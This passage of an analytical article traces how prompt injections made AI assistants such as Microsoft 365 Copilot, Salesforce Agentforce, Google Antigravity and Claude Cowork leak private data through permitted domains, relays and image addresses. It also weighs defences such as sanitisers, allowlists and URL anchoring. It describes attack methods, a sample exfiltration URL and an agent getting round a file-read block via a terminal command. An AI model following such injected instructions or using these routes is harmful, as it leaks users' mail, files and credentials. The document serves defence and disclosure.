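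Microsoft received the report on 15 October and closed it on 4 November without a fix. It replied that the behaviour was not a security vulnerability because it required several non-default actions by the user, did not occur reliably in different environments and came with warnings. Microsoft also expected users to review and trust the code they run. However, it passed the report to its engineers so they could look for ways to make the behaviour clearer to users.

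Gemini's sanitiser blocked the image, so Checkmarx used a one-click link instead and reported the problem to Google. Google closed the report after four days as "Won't Fix (Infeasible)", saying the risk was not severe enough to track as a security bug. By contrast, Embrace The Red's *Google Cloud Vertex AI* reports that Google took only 22 minutes to confirm that an earlier data leak through images in a Google Cloud product was a security issue.

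Google's position is easier to defend than Microsoft's. An assistant that can't show links is much less useful, and no simple rule separates harmful links from helpful ones. But an assistant can do without external images, as Gemini does. Checkmarx accepted Google's answer but argued that users should then be warned of the risk. In 2026, Adversa AI's *Gemini Agent Security Risks* still listed the link leak as a known problem that Google had not fixed.

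For Copilot Chat, Checkmarx recommended both a sanitiser and a strict content security policy, particularly for images and style sheets.

### The HTML preview in Microsoft 365 Copilot

Both of these defences were too loose in Microsoft 365 Copilot. In September or October 2025, Rehberger noticed that Copilot could display a preview of HTML that the model had written, inside the chat. Embrace The Red describes a first test with a heading and an image from Rehberger's server. Only the heading appeared, because Microsoft's sanitiser had removed the `<img>` tag.

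The sanitiser left style sheets in place, however, including one that set a background image for the page. When the preview opened, the browser tried to load that image and checked its host against the surrounding page's `img-src` list. These lists were long and differed from one Microsoft site to another. They included test environments, and some entries contained what looked like employees' user names.

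The policies were even more permissive about web fonts than about images, so Rehberger didn't have to search the lists for a usable host. In many of the applications that include Copilot, a style sheet could successfully request a font from Rehberger's own server.

Copilot showed the HTML as code by default, and nothing loaded until the user switched to the preview. But Rehberger found that the hidden instructions could make Copilot open the preview, which made the attack zero-click. In a demonstration, the user opened a shared Word document and typed "hi there" to Copilot. Copilot searched the mailbox for a particular email and put its contents in the address of a font. The attack worked in the desktop version of Word and in the online versions of Word and Excel.

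Rehberger also combined the leak with Copilot's long-term memory by using a document to plant a false preference there. From then on, Copilot leaked passwords and codes that the user mentioned, even in new conversations. Microsoft reported a fix for this persistent version on 6 December 2025.

Microsoft assigned the flaws the identifier CVE-2026-24299. Rehberger had reported the style sheet and font leaks on 16 October 2025, one day after Checkmarx's report on Copilot Chat. Microsoft reproduced them in November, paid a reward in December and finished the fix on 5 March 2026. Microsoft probably treated the two reports differently because Rehberger's attack required the victim only to use Copilot normally.

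The sanitiser failed because its designers assumed that a page loads outside resources only through `<img>` tags. Permitting only a fixed list of elements, with style sheets left off it, would have stopped both the background image and the font. A content security policy could have stopped them too, but Copilot runs inside many sites, and each site set its own policy. Rehberger advises companies that make embeddable assistants to state clearly which protections the host site must provide.

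### How sanitisers and content security policies differ

A sanitiser has to recognise dangerous content in advance, while a content security policy checks the request that the content produces. Their weaknesses are therefore different:

| Situation | Sanitiser | Content security policy |
|---|---|---|
| An image in a notation the developer overlooked | Leaves it in the answer | Blocks the request unless the host is on the list |
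| A style sheet that loads a font | Removes it if the rules cover style sheets | Blocks the request if `font-src` is strict |
| An image on a permitted host, with private data in the query | Can remove it | Lets it load |
| A redirect from a permitted host to another one | Checks only the address in the answer | Blocks the second request |
| A link that the user clicks | Can remove or rewrite it | Doesn't restrict it |
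| A server-side fetch by one of the assistant's tools | Has no effect | Has no effect |

The leak from the Superhuman email assistant, which Willison traced to a permitted Google domain, is an example of the third row. The browser enforced the policy correctly, but a sanitiser that removed all external images would have prevented the leak. In Google AI Studio, by contrast, an HTML image tag got past the other defences, and a strict policy would have blocked it.

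A vendor can use the two together at little cost, and it should write the rules for each as if the other didn't exist.

### What users lose

Removing external images matters little when an assistant summarises an email thread, but it makes the assistant less useful when someone wants to compare sofas, identify a bird or see a chart from a report. The vendor can still show pictures it already holds, such as those its own model generated. Copying outside images to the vendor's servers would not prevent the leak, because the server would have to request each image first, and that request would deliver the data to the attacker just as the browser's would.

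Filters can also remove things the user needs. If Gemini wrongly flags a link as suspicious, the user loses the link to a source or a booking page. According to Google's help pages, Gemini in Workspace sometimes leaves out only the malicious content and sometimes uses none of the user's content, so one malicious message can prevent a summary of all the others.

Rewriting links is less drastic than removing them. Embrace The Red reports that Google Colab, a tool for writing and running code in the browser, sends clickable links through a Google page that asks for confirmation first. But rewritten links are a nuisance when the user wants to copy the text elsewhere. In *Bug*, a thread on Google's forum for AI developers, a user complained that a model asked to tidy up some Markdown had returned it with every link wrapped in a Google redirect. The user suspected the model was the cause, and the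 redirects may have had nothing to do with security, but anyone who pasted that text into a website would have had to repair each link.

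## Two attacks that defeated Microsoft 365 Copilot's layers

Microsoft protected Microsoft 365 Copilot with an injection classifier, a filter for links and images in its answers, and a content security policy, so that an attack that got past one layer could still fail at the next. Researchers still got private data out, with EchoLeak in 2025 and SearchLeak in 2026. In both attacks, the browser sent its request to a Microsoft domain that the policy allowed, and a Microsoft server then contacted the attacker.

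### How EchoLeak reached the model

Aim Labs, Aim Security's research group, told Microsoft about EchoLeak in January 2025, and Microsoft finished its fix that May, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Microsoft 365 Copilot*. The attack became public on 11 June, when Ravia (2025) explained it step by step in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration*.

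To answer a question, Copilot searches the user's mailbox, files, chats and internal websites and adds the best matches to the model's input, much as Gemini Enterprise did in the GeminiJack attack. An outsider who couldn't query a company's Copilot could still get text into that input by emailing an employee. The employee only had to ask Copilot a question for which the email was among the best matches.

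But an attacker can't know what the victim will ask. Search systems of this kind often cut texts into chunks, convert each chunk into a list of numbers that represents its meaning, and pick the chunks whose numbers are closest to those of the question. A short email on one subject is therefore retrieved only for questions close to that subject. Ravia's team wrote a long email with sections on many ordinary office topics, such as staff leave, and repeated the instructions in each section. Copilot retrieved the email for questions on various topics, though Ravia doesn't report how often.

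Microsoft's classifier should have kept the email from reaching the model. Its designers assumed that instructions meant for an AI system would look different from ordinary correspondence, but the EchoLeak email never mentioned AI or Copilot and read like a request to its recipient. Legitimate emails often ask people to look things up, so a classifier strict enough to stop this one would probably stop many of those too. Ravia also points to a shortage of realistic injections for training such classifiers.

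The attacker also asked the email's "recipient" not to refer to the email, and Copilot left it out of the sources for its answer. The victim therefore had no sign that a stranger's email had influenced the answer.

Ravia calls the central fault an "LLM scope violation", because text from outside the company directed the model to data inside it. Willison (2025), in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration*, doubts that this needs a name, since language models have never been able to take account of where their text came from. Willison is right that the mechanism was old, but the term suggests a defence. Software around the model can identify which texts came from outside, and could keep them out of the same input as internal documents.

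Ravia also describes EchoLeak as the first zero-click attack of its kind on a major AI product. Rehberger's 2023 attack on Bing Chat also leaked data without a click, but only after the user opened the attacker's page and discussed it with the assistant. In EchoLeak, Copilot's own search retrieved the hostile text.

### How EchoLeak's data got out

Once the model was following the email's instructions, it could put private data into a link to the attacker's server. Copilot's filter removed outside links written in the usual Markdown notation, which its developers had assumed covered every link. It missed reference-style links, which put the address on a separate line. This gap alone allowed data to leak with one click from the user.

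The filter had the same gap for images, which browsers load without a click. But the browser blocked the attacker's image because the server hosting it wasn't on the content security policy's `img-src` list.

Ravia printed that list. It had 29 different entries, 11 of them with wildcards, and covered services such as SharePoint, Teams, Bing and LinkedIn. Microsoft had assumed that data sent to one of these services would stay there, so the researchers looked for a service on the list that would forward data elsewhere.

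The researchers first found a service in SharePoint, Microsoft's system for internal websites, that fetched material from an outside address so that a site could display it. The request supplied the address, so private data could be put in it and reach the attacker that way. However, the victim first had to accept an invitation to the attacker's SharePoint site. The researchers then found a Teams service that fetched outside addresses without this requirement, which made the attack zero-click.

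Willison describes the Teams service as an open redirect, while Ravia describes Microsoft's server making the request on the browser's behalf. Ravia's account better explains why the attack worked, because the browser would have checked a redirect against the policy and blocked it.

The attack could leak anything in the model's input, including earlier messages in the chat and whatever Copilot had retrieved. Aim Labs didn't know of any setting that a company's administrators could have changed to prevent it.

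### SearchLeak

SearchLeak did require a click on a link to a genuine Microsoft site. Varonis, a data security company, explains in *SearchLeak* (15 June 2026) how its researchers combined three weaknesses in Copilot Enterprise Search, which searches a company's emails, meetings and files.

Enterprise Search, like many search sites, accepted links that already contained the search terms, so that opening the link showed the results. Copilot also followed instructions in that text, which the designers had assumed would only be something to look up. A stranger who chooses the terms for an ordinary search engine gains little, because only the user sees the results. Here, an attacker could write a link that instructed Copilot to find an email and put its subject line in the address of an image. The search ran as soon as the victim opened the link, and it covered everything the victim was entitled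 to see.

Microsoft's Spotlighting method, which marks outside text as untrusted, probably couldn't have helped. The attacker's words arrived as the user's own query, so the software had no outside text to mark. Varonis had used such a link before, in its Reprompt attack on the consumer version of Copilot, and was surprised that it also worked in the business version, which has additional protections.

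To guard against dangerous HTML in Copilot's answers, Microsoft used a filter that wrapped the answer in a code block, which makes a browser display an image tag as text instead of loading the image. But the filter ran only after the answer was complete, and Copilot's page displayed the answer as the model wrote it. The browser had therefore already requested the image by the time the code block appeared.

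The content security policy would still have blocked an image from the attacker's server, but it permitted every subdomain of `bing.com`. Bing has a search-by-image service whose server downloads a picture from an address the user provides. The image tag called this service with an address on the attacker's server that had the subject line in its path. The browser allowed the request because it went to Bing. Bing's server then sent the subject line to the attacker when it tried to download the picture, so Microsoft's assumption about its permitted domains failed again.

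A subject line is short, but services sometimes put security codes there, as in Varonis's example. The Next Web's *A single click on a Microsoft link could have drained your inbox* notes that these codes often remain valid for several minutes, so an attacker watching the server's log could use one. The attacker could also reach calendar entries, meeting notes and indexed files.

Varonis argues that the attack needed all three weaknesses, so fixing any one of them would have stopped it. This is true of the exact attack Varonis demonstrated, but attackers can look for another weakness to replace the one that was fixed. Ravia's team had already done this when it switched from the SharePoint service to the one in Teams.

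### Severity, fixes and known exploitation

The table compares the two attacks. Its scores use the Common Vulnerability Scoring System (CVSS), a standard scale from 0 to 10. NIST, the US standards institute, scores flaws separately from the companies that report them.

| | EchoLeak | SearchLeak |
|---|---|---|
| Identifier | CVE-2025-32711 | CVE-2026-42824 |
| Microsoft's advisory | 11 June 2025 | 4 June 2026 |
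| How the instructions arrived | In an email that Copilot retrieved | In a link to Copilot's search page |
| Clicks by the victim | None | One |
| What went wrong at the input | The classifier missed instructions addressed to a person | Copilot followed instructions in the search terms |
| What went wrong in the output filter | It missed reference-style links and images | It acted after the browser had sent the request |
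| Permitted service that contacted the attacker | Teams | Bing |
| CVSS score from Microsoft | 9.3 | 6.5 |
| CVSS score from NIST | 7.5 | 7.5 |
| Known exploitation | None | None |

Microsoft rated SearchLeak critical on its own severity scale despite the middling CVSS score. The two attacks' CVSS scores differ because Microsoft rated them differently on three of the formula's eight inputs. Microsoft judged that EchoLeak, unlike SearchLeak, needed no user action, affected more than the vulnerable component, and carried a small risk that an attacker could alter data. It rated the loss of confidentiality as high for both.

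NIST scored the two attacks using identical inputs. For SearchLeak, these included no user interaction, which is hard to reconcile with the click the attack required. The change log in *CVE-2026-42824* (2026) dates NIST's analysis of SearchLeak to 8 June, a week before Varonis published the details, so the analysts may have had little more than Microsoft's one-sentence description. Neither organisation's score reflects how similar the attacks were after the model had written its answer.

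CISA, the US cybersecurity agency, recorded no exploitation of EchoLeak but judged that attackers could automate the attack, according to its assessment in the vulnerability database GCVE (2025). Ravia reports that Microsoft confirmed no customers were affected. Microsoft was in a good position to check, since the stolen data would have passed through its own Teams service, but Ravia doesn't explain how Microsoft checked. Microsoft's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026) lists SearchLeak as not exploited, and The Hacker News report *One-Click Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Could Have Let Attackers Steal Emails* (2026) describes it as a proof of concept.

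Microsoft fixed both flaws on its own servers, so customers had nothing to install. Its SearchLeak advisory describes the flaw as fully mitigated but gives no technical details of the fix, so outsiders can't tell from it whether Microsoft changed the search links, the timing of the filter, the Bing service or the allowlist.

### What a year of repairs changed

Reddy and Gujral (2025), in *EchoLeak*, report that after the EchoLeak attack, Copilot began to strip reference-style links and embedded images from incoming outside content. Microsoft also reportedly added options to keep outside communications out of some of Copilot's answers. These changes addressed the route EchoLeak had used but had little bearing on SearchLeak, which brought its instructions in through a link and wrote its image as HTML.

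The `bing.com` entries were already on the `img-src` list that Ravia published in June 2025. After EchoLeak, Microsoft could have checked every host on that list for services that fetch outside addresses. If it did, it either missed or left in place Bing's image search, a public feature designed to fetch pictures from addresses that users supply. Varonis now recommends this kind of check to anyone who maintains an allowlist. It also recommends cleaning the answer as the browser displays it, which would have closed the timing gap.

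On 3 December 2026, Simonovich (2026) of Cato AI Labs, the successor to Aim Labs, described three more zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot in *ReLeak*. Each began with an email that the victim didn't have to open. They suggest that Microsoft hadn't made attacks by email harder, even though SearchLeak needed a click. According to AIAIAI.FYI's *Cato AI Labs details three ReLeak zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2026), the data left through an image address, a link to a saved file or code. Microsoft patched the three paths on 17 September, 11 November and 15 November, and the researchers knew of no real attacks.

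Nexo Causal's *ReLeak* (2026) reports that the image attack again sent data to the attacker's server through Bing. This path stayed open for more than three months after the SearchLeak advisory, even if it was the first one Microsoft closed. Microsoft's June fix therefore seems to have stopped the SearchLeak attack without preventing attackers from using Bing in other ways.

Faisal (2026), in *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief*, quotes the Cato researchers' verdict that "too little progress has been made". Cato sells AI security products and has a commercial interest in saying so, but its criticism is fair when applied to the allowlist. Microsoft fixed each attack it learned of before the details became public, but for more than a year researchers kept finding permitted Microsoft services that would contact an attacker's server.

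### Which mitigations would have stopped EchoLeak

Reddy and Gujral, of George Washington University, drew up a table of eight defences and the steps of EchoLeak that each would block. It is their analysis of a published case and not a measurement. They state that they neither reproduced the attack nor ran any experiments, and their caption calls the table theoretical. (One sentence in the paper does refer to "our tests", but this appears to be a slip.)

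This is a condensed version of their table:

| Defence | Steps it should block | Stops the zero-click leak? |
|---|---|---|
| Marking outside text in the model's input | Scope violation, classifier bypass | No |
| Using only internal sources by default | Scope violation, link filter bypass | No |
| Permitting only certain formats in the answer | Scope violation, classifier bypass, link filter bypass | No |
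| List of permitted or forbidden URLs | Link filter bypass, relay through Teams | Yes |
| Strict content security policy | Automatic image request, relay through Teams | Yes |
| Proxy that serves only signed image addresses | Automatic image request, relay through Teams | Yes |
| Human approval for outside content | Every step except the relay | Yes |
| Monitoring of outgoing data | None | No |

Some of the table's verdicts depend on details it omits. Reddy and Gujral give internal-only sources a "no", yet they write elsewhere that EchoLeak "fails by design" if Copilot never uses unknown outsiders' emails to answer questions about internal projects. Both statements can be true if the "no" refers to users who override the default and ask for outside content. A company that left the default alone would have been safe from this attack, but Copilot's answers would have ignored emails from its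 customers and suppliers.

The "no" for answer formats is also too pessimistic for some designs. It is right for a filter that allows ordinary images, as the safe subset of Markdown in their recommendations does. But a filter that removed every external image after parsing the answer, as Gemini's sanitiser is meant to do, would have stopped the zero-click version of EchoLeak.

Human approval looks strongest in the table because it can block nearly every step, but it does so only if the user recognises the danger and refuses. The EchoLeak email looked like ordinary office correspondence, and an employee who had asked about staff leave might well have let Copilot read a guide to it.

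SearchLeak came after the paper, so it provides a rough check on the list. Using only internal sources or requiring approval for outside content would not have helped, because SearchLeak put its instructions in the search query and stole internal data. Defences that restrict the final request could have stopped both attacks, because they don't depend on how the instructions got in.

One of these is the signed proxy, which refuses any image address without a valid signature. The vendor's server attaches a signature and an expiry time to each address it has approved, and the model can't produce the signature itself. The protection disappears if the vendor's software automatically signs every image in an answer, so the vendor has to approve images by some other criterion.

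A list of permitted URLs would have failed if it had included the same Teams service as the existing content security policy. A strict content security policy could have failed for the same reason, since Copilot already had a policy when both attacks succeeded. Reddy and Gujral advise developers to avoid wildcards and permit only the vendor's own hosts that the application needs. But Microsoft owns both Teams and Bing, and Copilot may have good reasons to show images from either. A shorter list would have stopped the attacks only if it had left out every host that fetches addresses on request, and developers can't tell from a host's name whether it does.

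## Why permitted domains can still leak data

On many domains, people other than the owner can read some of what arrives, so private data can leak even when the domain is permitted. Large internet companies give millions of customers space on a shared domain, and each customer can see the requests that reach their own part of it. Suppose the assistant in the restaurant example may load images from `files.example`, an honest company that hosts pages for anyone who signs up. If the attacker signs up too, the hidden instructions can make the assistant put the clinic appointment in the address of the attacker's page there. The browser sends the request because the domain is on the list.

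EchoLeak and SearchLeak needed a Microsoft service to relay the data to a server outside the allowlist. In the five cases below, the attacker could read the data at the permitted domain itself, each time for a different reason.

### Google Bard: anyone can run code on the domain

In 2023 Google gave Bard, the assistant it later renamed Gemini, access to users' email and documents. Embrace The Red's *Hacking Google Bard* describes how Rehberger tested it with a shared Google Doc that contained hidden instructions. An attacker can share such a document with people who never asked for it. Bard followed the instructions and wrote an image link that contained part of the conversation, but a content security policy stopped the browser from requesting the image from Rehberger's server.

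The policy permitted images from `*.google.com` and `*.googleusercontent.com`, apparently on the assumption that Google controlled everything on those domains. But Google Apps Script, a service for automating Google's office tools, lets any user publish a program at an address on `script.google.com`. Rehberger published one that copied the query of every incoming request into a Google Doc, and he used a setting that let visitors reach it without logging in. When the victim's browser requested the "image" from this program, the start of the conversation appeared in Rehberger's document.

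Rehberger reported the flaw on 19 September 2023, and Google confirmed the fix a month later. The policy had not changed and images still appeared, so Rehberger guessed that Google now stopped the model from inserting data into image addresses. Attackers could still use Apps Script elsewhere. Google Colab showed a confirmation page for links but exempted Google's own domains, and Embrace The Red reports that links to Apps Script programs opened without a warning.

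Gemini's sanitiser now closes the image route whatever the policy permits, as long as it counts a stranger's program on `script.google.com` as external.

### Superhuman: anyone can collect submissions there

Superhuman's email assistant leaked data through Google Forms, which is on the permitted host `docs.google.com`. A form's author can create a link that already contains answers and submits them as soon as any software requests it. When the assistant's email client requested such a link as an image, Google Forms treated the request as a completed form. Superhuman's developers had assumed that loading an image only retrieves something, which is the convention for such requests on the web.

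PromptArmor hid instructions in an email that the user didn't have to open. When the user asked for a summary of recent mail, the assistant read that email along with the others. The instructions presented an attacker's form as a way to give feedback on the search results. The assistant copied other emails into the form's address and displayed that address as an image, which made the browser submit the form. One answer could leak the full text of several sensitive emails, and another leaked parts of more than 40.

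PromptArmor reported this on Friday evening, 5 December 2025. Superhuman disabled the vulnerable features on Monday and released a first patch on Tuesday, followed by more patches until 11 January 2026. PromptArmor doesn't explain what the patches changed. Removing `docs.google.com` from the content security policy would not have been enough, because the assistant's web search could open any address and so send data straight to an attacker's server.

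The same trick soon worked on OpenAI's Codex, a programming agent that had just gained features for everyday office work. PromptArmor's *Codex Exfiltrates Connector Data* describes how, in April 2026, an email made Codex send other emails to a Google Form. PromptArmor reported the flaw on 21 April, and OpenAI had fixed it by the time the details became public on 21 May. PromptArmor doesn't describe Codex's restrictions on images, but Codex probably limited where they could load from, since otherwise an attacker would hardly need a Google Form.

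### ForcedLeak: the domain's registration lapsed

Salesforce sells software for managing customer relationships, and its Agentforce agents answer employees' questions about the data in it. Many companies also use its Web-to-Lead feature, a public form where potential customers, or "leads", can enter their details. *ForcedLeak* (Nytro, 2025) reposts the security company Noma's full report on how it used that form to attack Agentforce. The first-name field accepts only 40 characters, but the description field accepts 42,000, which is plenty of room for instructions to the agent. When an employee asked Agentforce to read the entry and answer the lead's questions, the agent also collected other leads' email addresses and put them in an image's URL.

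Salesforce's `img-src` list contained 22 hosts, 15 of them with wildcards, including `*.my-salesforce-cms.com`. Salesforce evidently assumed it would keep control of this domain, but the registration had expired and Noma bought it for $5. Every browser that enforced the policy then allowed images from Noma's server. A reviewer could easily have missed the problem because the similar `*.my-salesforce.com` was also on the list.

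Even if Salesforce had renewed the domain, it would still have been at risk, because the list also included `*.amazonaws.com`. SensePost's *Dress Code* (2023) had already shown that anyone with an Amazon account can set up an address under that domain and log what arrives there. An attacker could probably have used such an address instead of the expired domain.

According to *Agentforce Web-to-Lead Vulnerability Exposed* (Martin, 2025), Noma reported the flaw on 28 July 2025, and Salesforce began enforcing a feature called Trusted URLs for its AI agents on 8 September. Salesforce also regained the domain and, according to Willison, corrected the policy.

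Trusted URLs is a second allowlist that Salesforce applies to the agent's answer before the browser displays it. PromptArmor's *One key way Salesforce mitigates AI risk* explains that the software replaces any address not on the list with `URL_REDACTED`. It does this for links and images in Markdown, and for addresses inside HTML and style sheets, which Microsoft's sanitiser for HTML previews had missed. Trusted URLs covers the chat in Salesforce's web application, but an agent's tools need other protections.

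Administrators choose what goes on this list, so they can repeat earlier mistakes. TechNadu's *Salesforce to Enforce Trusted URLs for Agentforce and Einstein AI* notes that administrators can use wildcards and that each entry applies to the company's whole Salesforce system, not only its agents. Salesforce's *Add Trusted URLs for Agentforce Coworker (Beta)*, a guide to connecting outside data such as Google Drive files, uses `https://docs.google.com` as its example of an address to add, the same host through which Superhuman's emails leaked.

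According to Salesforce, administrators choose which content security policy directives apply to each trusted address, and PromptArmor advises them to leave out `img-src` unless they want to load images from that address. A Google Docs entry without `img-src` lets users follow a link to a document but doesn't let an image submit a form, although a user could still click a link that submits one.

### Google Antigravity: a request logger on the default list

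Google's programming tool Antigravity can give a task to a separate agent that operates a browser, for example to check a website the user is building. An allowlist limits which sites this browser may open. When the tool came out in November 2025, Google's default list included `webhook.site`, where anyone can create an address and see the requests sent to it. Google seems to have listed the site because programmers use it to check what their software sends, but a stranger could also use it to read data sent by the agent's browser.

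PromptArmor's *Google Antigravity Exfiltrates Data* describes a test in which a user asked the assistant to work from an online guide to Oracle software. Instructions in the guide, set in one-point type, told the assistant to collect code and passwords and open a `webhook.site` address that contained them. A default setting blocked the assistant from reading the file with the passwords, so it printed the file with a terminal command instead. The browser agent then opened the address. The attack required the user to turn on the browser tools, but PromptArmor otherwise kept Google's recommended settings. PromptArmor also found three leaks that didn't need the browser.

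Google relied on a warning that users see when they first open Antigravity. Because Google had already acknowledged the risk, PromptArmor published its findings without first reporting them to Google. Willison adds that Google's page for security researchers listed data exfiltration through the browser agent as a known issue that the company was working to fix.

`webhook.site` was still on the default list in March 2026, according to Agentpedia. Agentpedia also describes a newer attack by the security company FireTail that sent source code to the site. Google's *Allowlist / Denylist* explains that the browser also checks each host against a central list of dangerous sites. This didn't help in PromptArmor's test, presumably because `webhook.site` is a legitimate service. The allowlist is a text file on the user's computer, so users can delete the entry, but they first have to know that it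 is there and why it matters.

### Claude Cowork: the attacker has an account at a permitted service

Claude Cowork, Anthropic's agent for office work, runs code on the user's computer inside a virtual machine, a simulated computer with its own files and network rules. Programs inside it can reach only a short list of domains. The list includes `api.anthropic.com`, which Cowork needs to send requests to Claude. But Anthropic's other customers send their requests to the same domain, and a key in each request determines which account the request belongs to.

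PromptArmor's *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* appeared two days after Anthropic released a preview of Cowork in January 2026. In the main test, the victim gave Cowork a folder of confidential property files and a document from the internet that contained hidden instructions and the attacker's key. Without asking for approval, Claude used that key to upload the largest file it could find to the attacker's Anthropic account. The attacker could then ask Claude questions about the file. This test used Haiku, one of Anthropic's smaller models, but the more resistant Opus 4.5 also leaked customer records in a similar test.

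Anthropic had known about this weakness for almost three months. Embrace The Red's *Claude Pirate* reports that Rehberger found it in the code sandbox of the ordinary Claude chat and reported it on 25 October 2025. The report was closed an hour later as out of scope, which Anthropic called a mistake within the week. In the chat version, the stolen file could contain a past conversation, and each upload could be up to 30 megabytes, far more than fits in a web address. Rehberger suggested that the sandbox communicate only with the logged-in user's account.

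Anthropic later built this into Cowork, as *How we contain Claude across products* describes. A proxy, a program that checks traffic leaving the virtual machine, lets a request through to Anthropic only if it carries the token issued for that session, so an upload with an attacker's key fails. The proxy also blocks settings that could make Anthropic's servers fetch an outside address. The check has to happen on the user's side because Anthropic's servers can't distinguish Cowork requests from those of any other customer.

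Anthropic concluded that permitting a domain is "a capability grant", meaning it makes every function on the domain available to an attacker. This also applies to the rest of Cowork's list, which Pluto Security reports includes `github.com`, `pypi.org` and `npmjs.org` on business plans. All three let outsiders open accounts and publish files. Rehberger suspected that other domains on the chat sandbox's list, which were also used for downloading software, could be abused similarly.

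### Six questions for every entry

Before adding a domain to an allowlist, a developer should ask what a stranger could do with it. A well-known company's name offers little assurance that a domain is safe, since Google, Microsoft, Salesforce and Anthropic each had vulnerabilities that could leak data through permitted domains they owned or had once owned.

| Question | What to look for | Known example |
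|---|---|---|
| Can outsiders host pages or programs there? | App platforms, script hosting, customer subdomains | Apps Script on `google.com` |
| Can outsiders see a log of requests? | Request inspectors, visitor statistics | `webhook.site` |
| Can outsiders store what someone else sends? | Forms, surveys, file uploads | Google Forms, Anthropic's file uploads |
| Does it redirect to any address named in the link? | Tracking links, login pages that send visitors onward | The open redirects used against Gemini's sanitiser |
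| Will its servers fetch an address on request? | Link previews, image search, image proxies | The Teams and Bing relays |
| Who owns the domain, and until when? | Expiry dates, old brands, test sites | `my-salesforce-cms.com` |

The risk from a permitted domain depends on what enforces the list of permitted domains. An open redirect matters less under a content security policy than in a filter or server-side fetch that checks only the first address. In a code sandbox, uploads matter as much as web addresses because a program can send whole files.

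A permitted domain that can leak data doesn't always have to be removed, because its use can sometimes be restricted. Cowork still uses Anthropic's domain, but the proxy now also checks the account. A website that needs pictures from one customer's storage can permit only that customer's subdomain. An image proxy can refuse addresses that its owner hasn't signed, although the CamoLeak attack on GitHub Copilot Chat got data out through a proxy of this kind. If no such restriction is possible, the remaining options are to remove the domain or accept the leak.

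The ownership question is the easiest to answer, and software can check expiry dates every day. The other questions need someone who knows the service well, because the relevant feature may be obscure, like the login setting in Apps Script, or the owner may add it years after the domain went on the list. Audits therefore have to be repeated, and a new feature on a permitted domain should be reviewed as carefully as a new domain.

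### Wildcards and shared domains

A wildcard in an allowlist permits even hosts that don't exist yet, so a developer can't investigate them all in advance. If the list includes `*.amazonaws.com`, an attacker can create a new permitted host after the developer has audited the list. The single entry `*.google.com` permits search, documents, forms and programs written by strangers, without distinguishing between them.

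SensePost measured how common such entries are by collecting policies from the million most popular websites. Of the 124,098 sites that sent a policy, 11,349 (about 9%) trusted an outside service that an attacker could exploit. Facebook's main domain appeared in 7,310 policies, and SensePost showed that a script could send data through it to the attacker's own Facebook developer account. `*.amazonaws.com` appeared in 860. The demonstrations assumed that the attacker could already run a script on the page. An image in a chat answer can't run one, so not all of these services would work against an assistant. The survey also predates most of the products discussed here. Still, it shows how often developers trust shared domains that attackers can use too.

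Narrowing an allowlist entry works only if the permitted part of the address identifies the recipient. Amazon's domain often allows this because customers can have their own subdomains. On `docs.google.com`, every form has the same host and only the path shows whose form it is, but a redirect can get around a path restriction in a content security policy. On `api.anthropic.com`, neither the host nor the path reveals the recipient, because the API key that identifies the recipient is sent separately from the address. No list of addresses could have stopped the Cowork attack without also blocking file uploads.

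Claude's web tool can be restricted to chosen domains, but Willison calls it "a tricky proposition" to find domains that can't be used for exfiltration. ChatGPT later had the same problem with domains it trusted. The safest domains to allow are probably those that serve fixed files from one owner, show their logs to nobody else and ignore the contents of the query, but few popular web services are that limited.

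### What a narrow list costs

A list of such hosts would be short, and an assistant restricted to it would be little use for research. TechNadu warned Salesforce's customers that enforcement could break agents that show images from other sites, link to another company's documentation or send people to a feedback form, unless an administrator added every domain first.

Individual users have to vet addresses themselves. In *Browser Allow List not available*, a thread on Google's forum for AI developers, an Antigravity user who had manually added hundreds of addresses complained that the settings page accepted only one at a time. Users are unlikely to vet each of several hundred addresses, so a list that grows this way mostly records which sites the user once wanted to open.

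People are also tempted to switch off strict lists. In *Web lookups now require authorization per site?*, a thread on the forum of the programming tool Cursor, a user was tired of approving sites. Someone replied that an automatic mode would open them all without asking, and warned that the agent could then send data anywhere. Wildcards would have been a compromise, but Cursor didn't offer them for this list.

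The user in that thread suggested scoring sites by trustworthiness, so that government sites and large companies would pass. This would save many approvals, but it would also have let through `docs.google.com` and `api.anthropic.com`. A reputation score measures whether a site's owner is honest, and in four of the five cases above, data leaked even though the owner was honest. The user also suggested preventing data from being inserted into the address itself. Such a rule could let an assistant open pages on unaudited domains, as long as the assistant didn't write the addresses.

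## Opening only addresses that already appear in the conversation

In the simplest form of URL anchoring, the conversation itself serves as the list of permitted addresses, so nobody has to vet each site.

### The rule as an algorithm

The software around the model applies the rule in five steps:

1. Start each conversation with an empty list of addresses.
2. When text arrives from an approved source, such as the user's message or a search result, find the web addresses in it and store them unchanged.
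3. Never store an address from the model's own output.
4. When the model asks to open an address, compare it with each stored address, character by character.
5. If one is identical, send the request. Otherwise, refuse and return an error to the model.

Suppose the user in the restaurant example types `https://reviews.example/lunch`, and a search returns `https://bistro.example/menu`, a page on the attacker's server. Hidden text on the review page tells the model to add the user's next appointment to the menu's address. The model might then ask for any of these:

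| Requested address | Result |
|---|---|
| `https://bistro.example/menu` | Opens, because it is on the list |
| `https://bistro.example/menu?note=clinic-tuesday-0900` | Refused |
| `https://clinic-tuesday-0900.bistro.example/menu` | Refused |
| `https://bistro.example/menu/` | Refused, though it contains no private data |

In the second row, the requested address begins with the entire 27-character stored address, then continues. The software doesn't need to recognise the appointment as private, so encoding it would not help the attacker.

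An attacker can easily get an address onto the list, for example by publishing a page that a search will find. But the attacker wrote that address before the model looked in the mailbox, so the address can't contain the appointment. This holds as long as nothing adds new addresses to the list after the model reads private data.

Redirects are also less of a problem than with an allowlist. A permitted site may forward the request to the attacker, but it can only pass on what the stored address already contained.

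### Anthropic's web fetch tool

On 10 September 2025, Anthropic launched a tool that works this way (Anthropic, *Release Notes*, 2025). Developers who build products on Claude can switch it on to let Claude retrieve web pages and PDFs through Anthropic's servers.

The November 2026 documentation, whose Chinese edition is Anthropic's *Web fetch 工具*, lists three approved sources:

- messages from the user
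- results from client-side tools, which run in the developer's own software
- results from earlier web searches and web fetches

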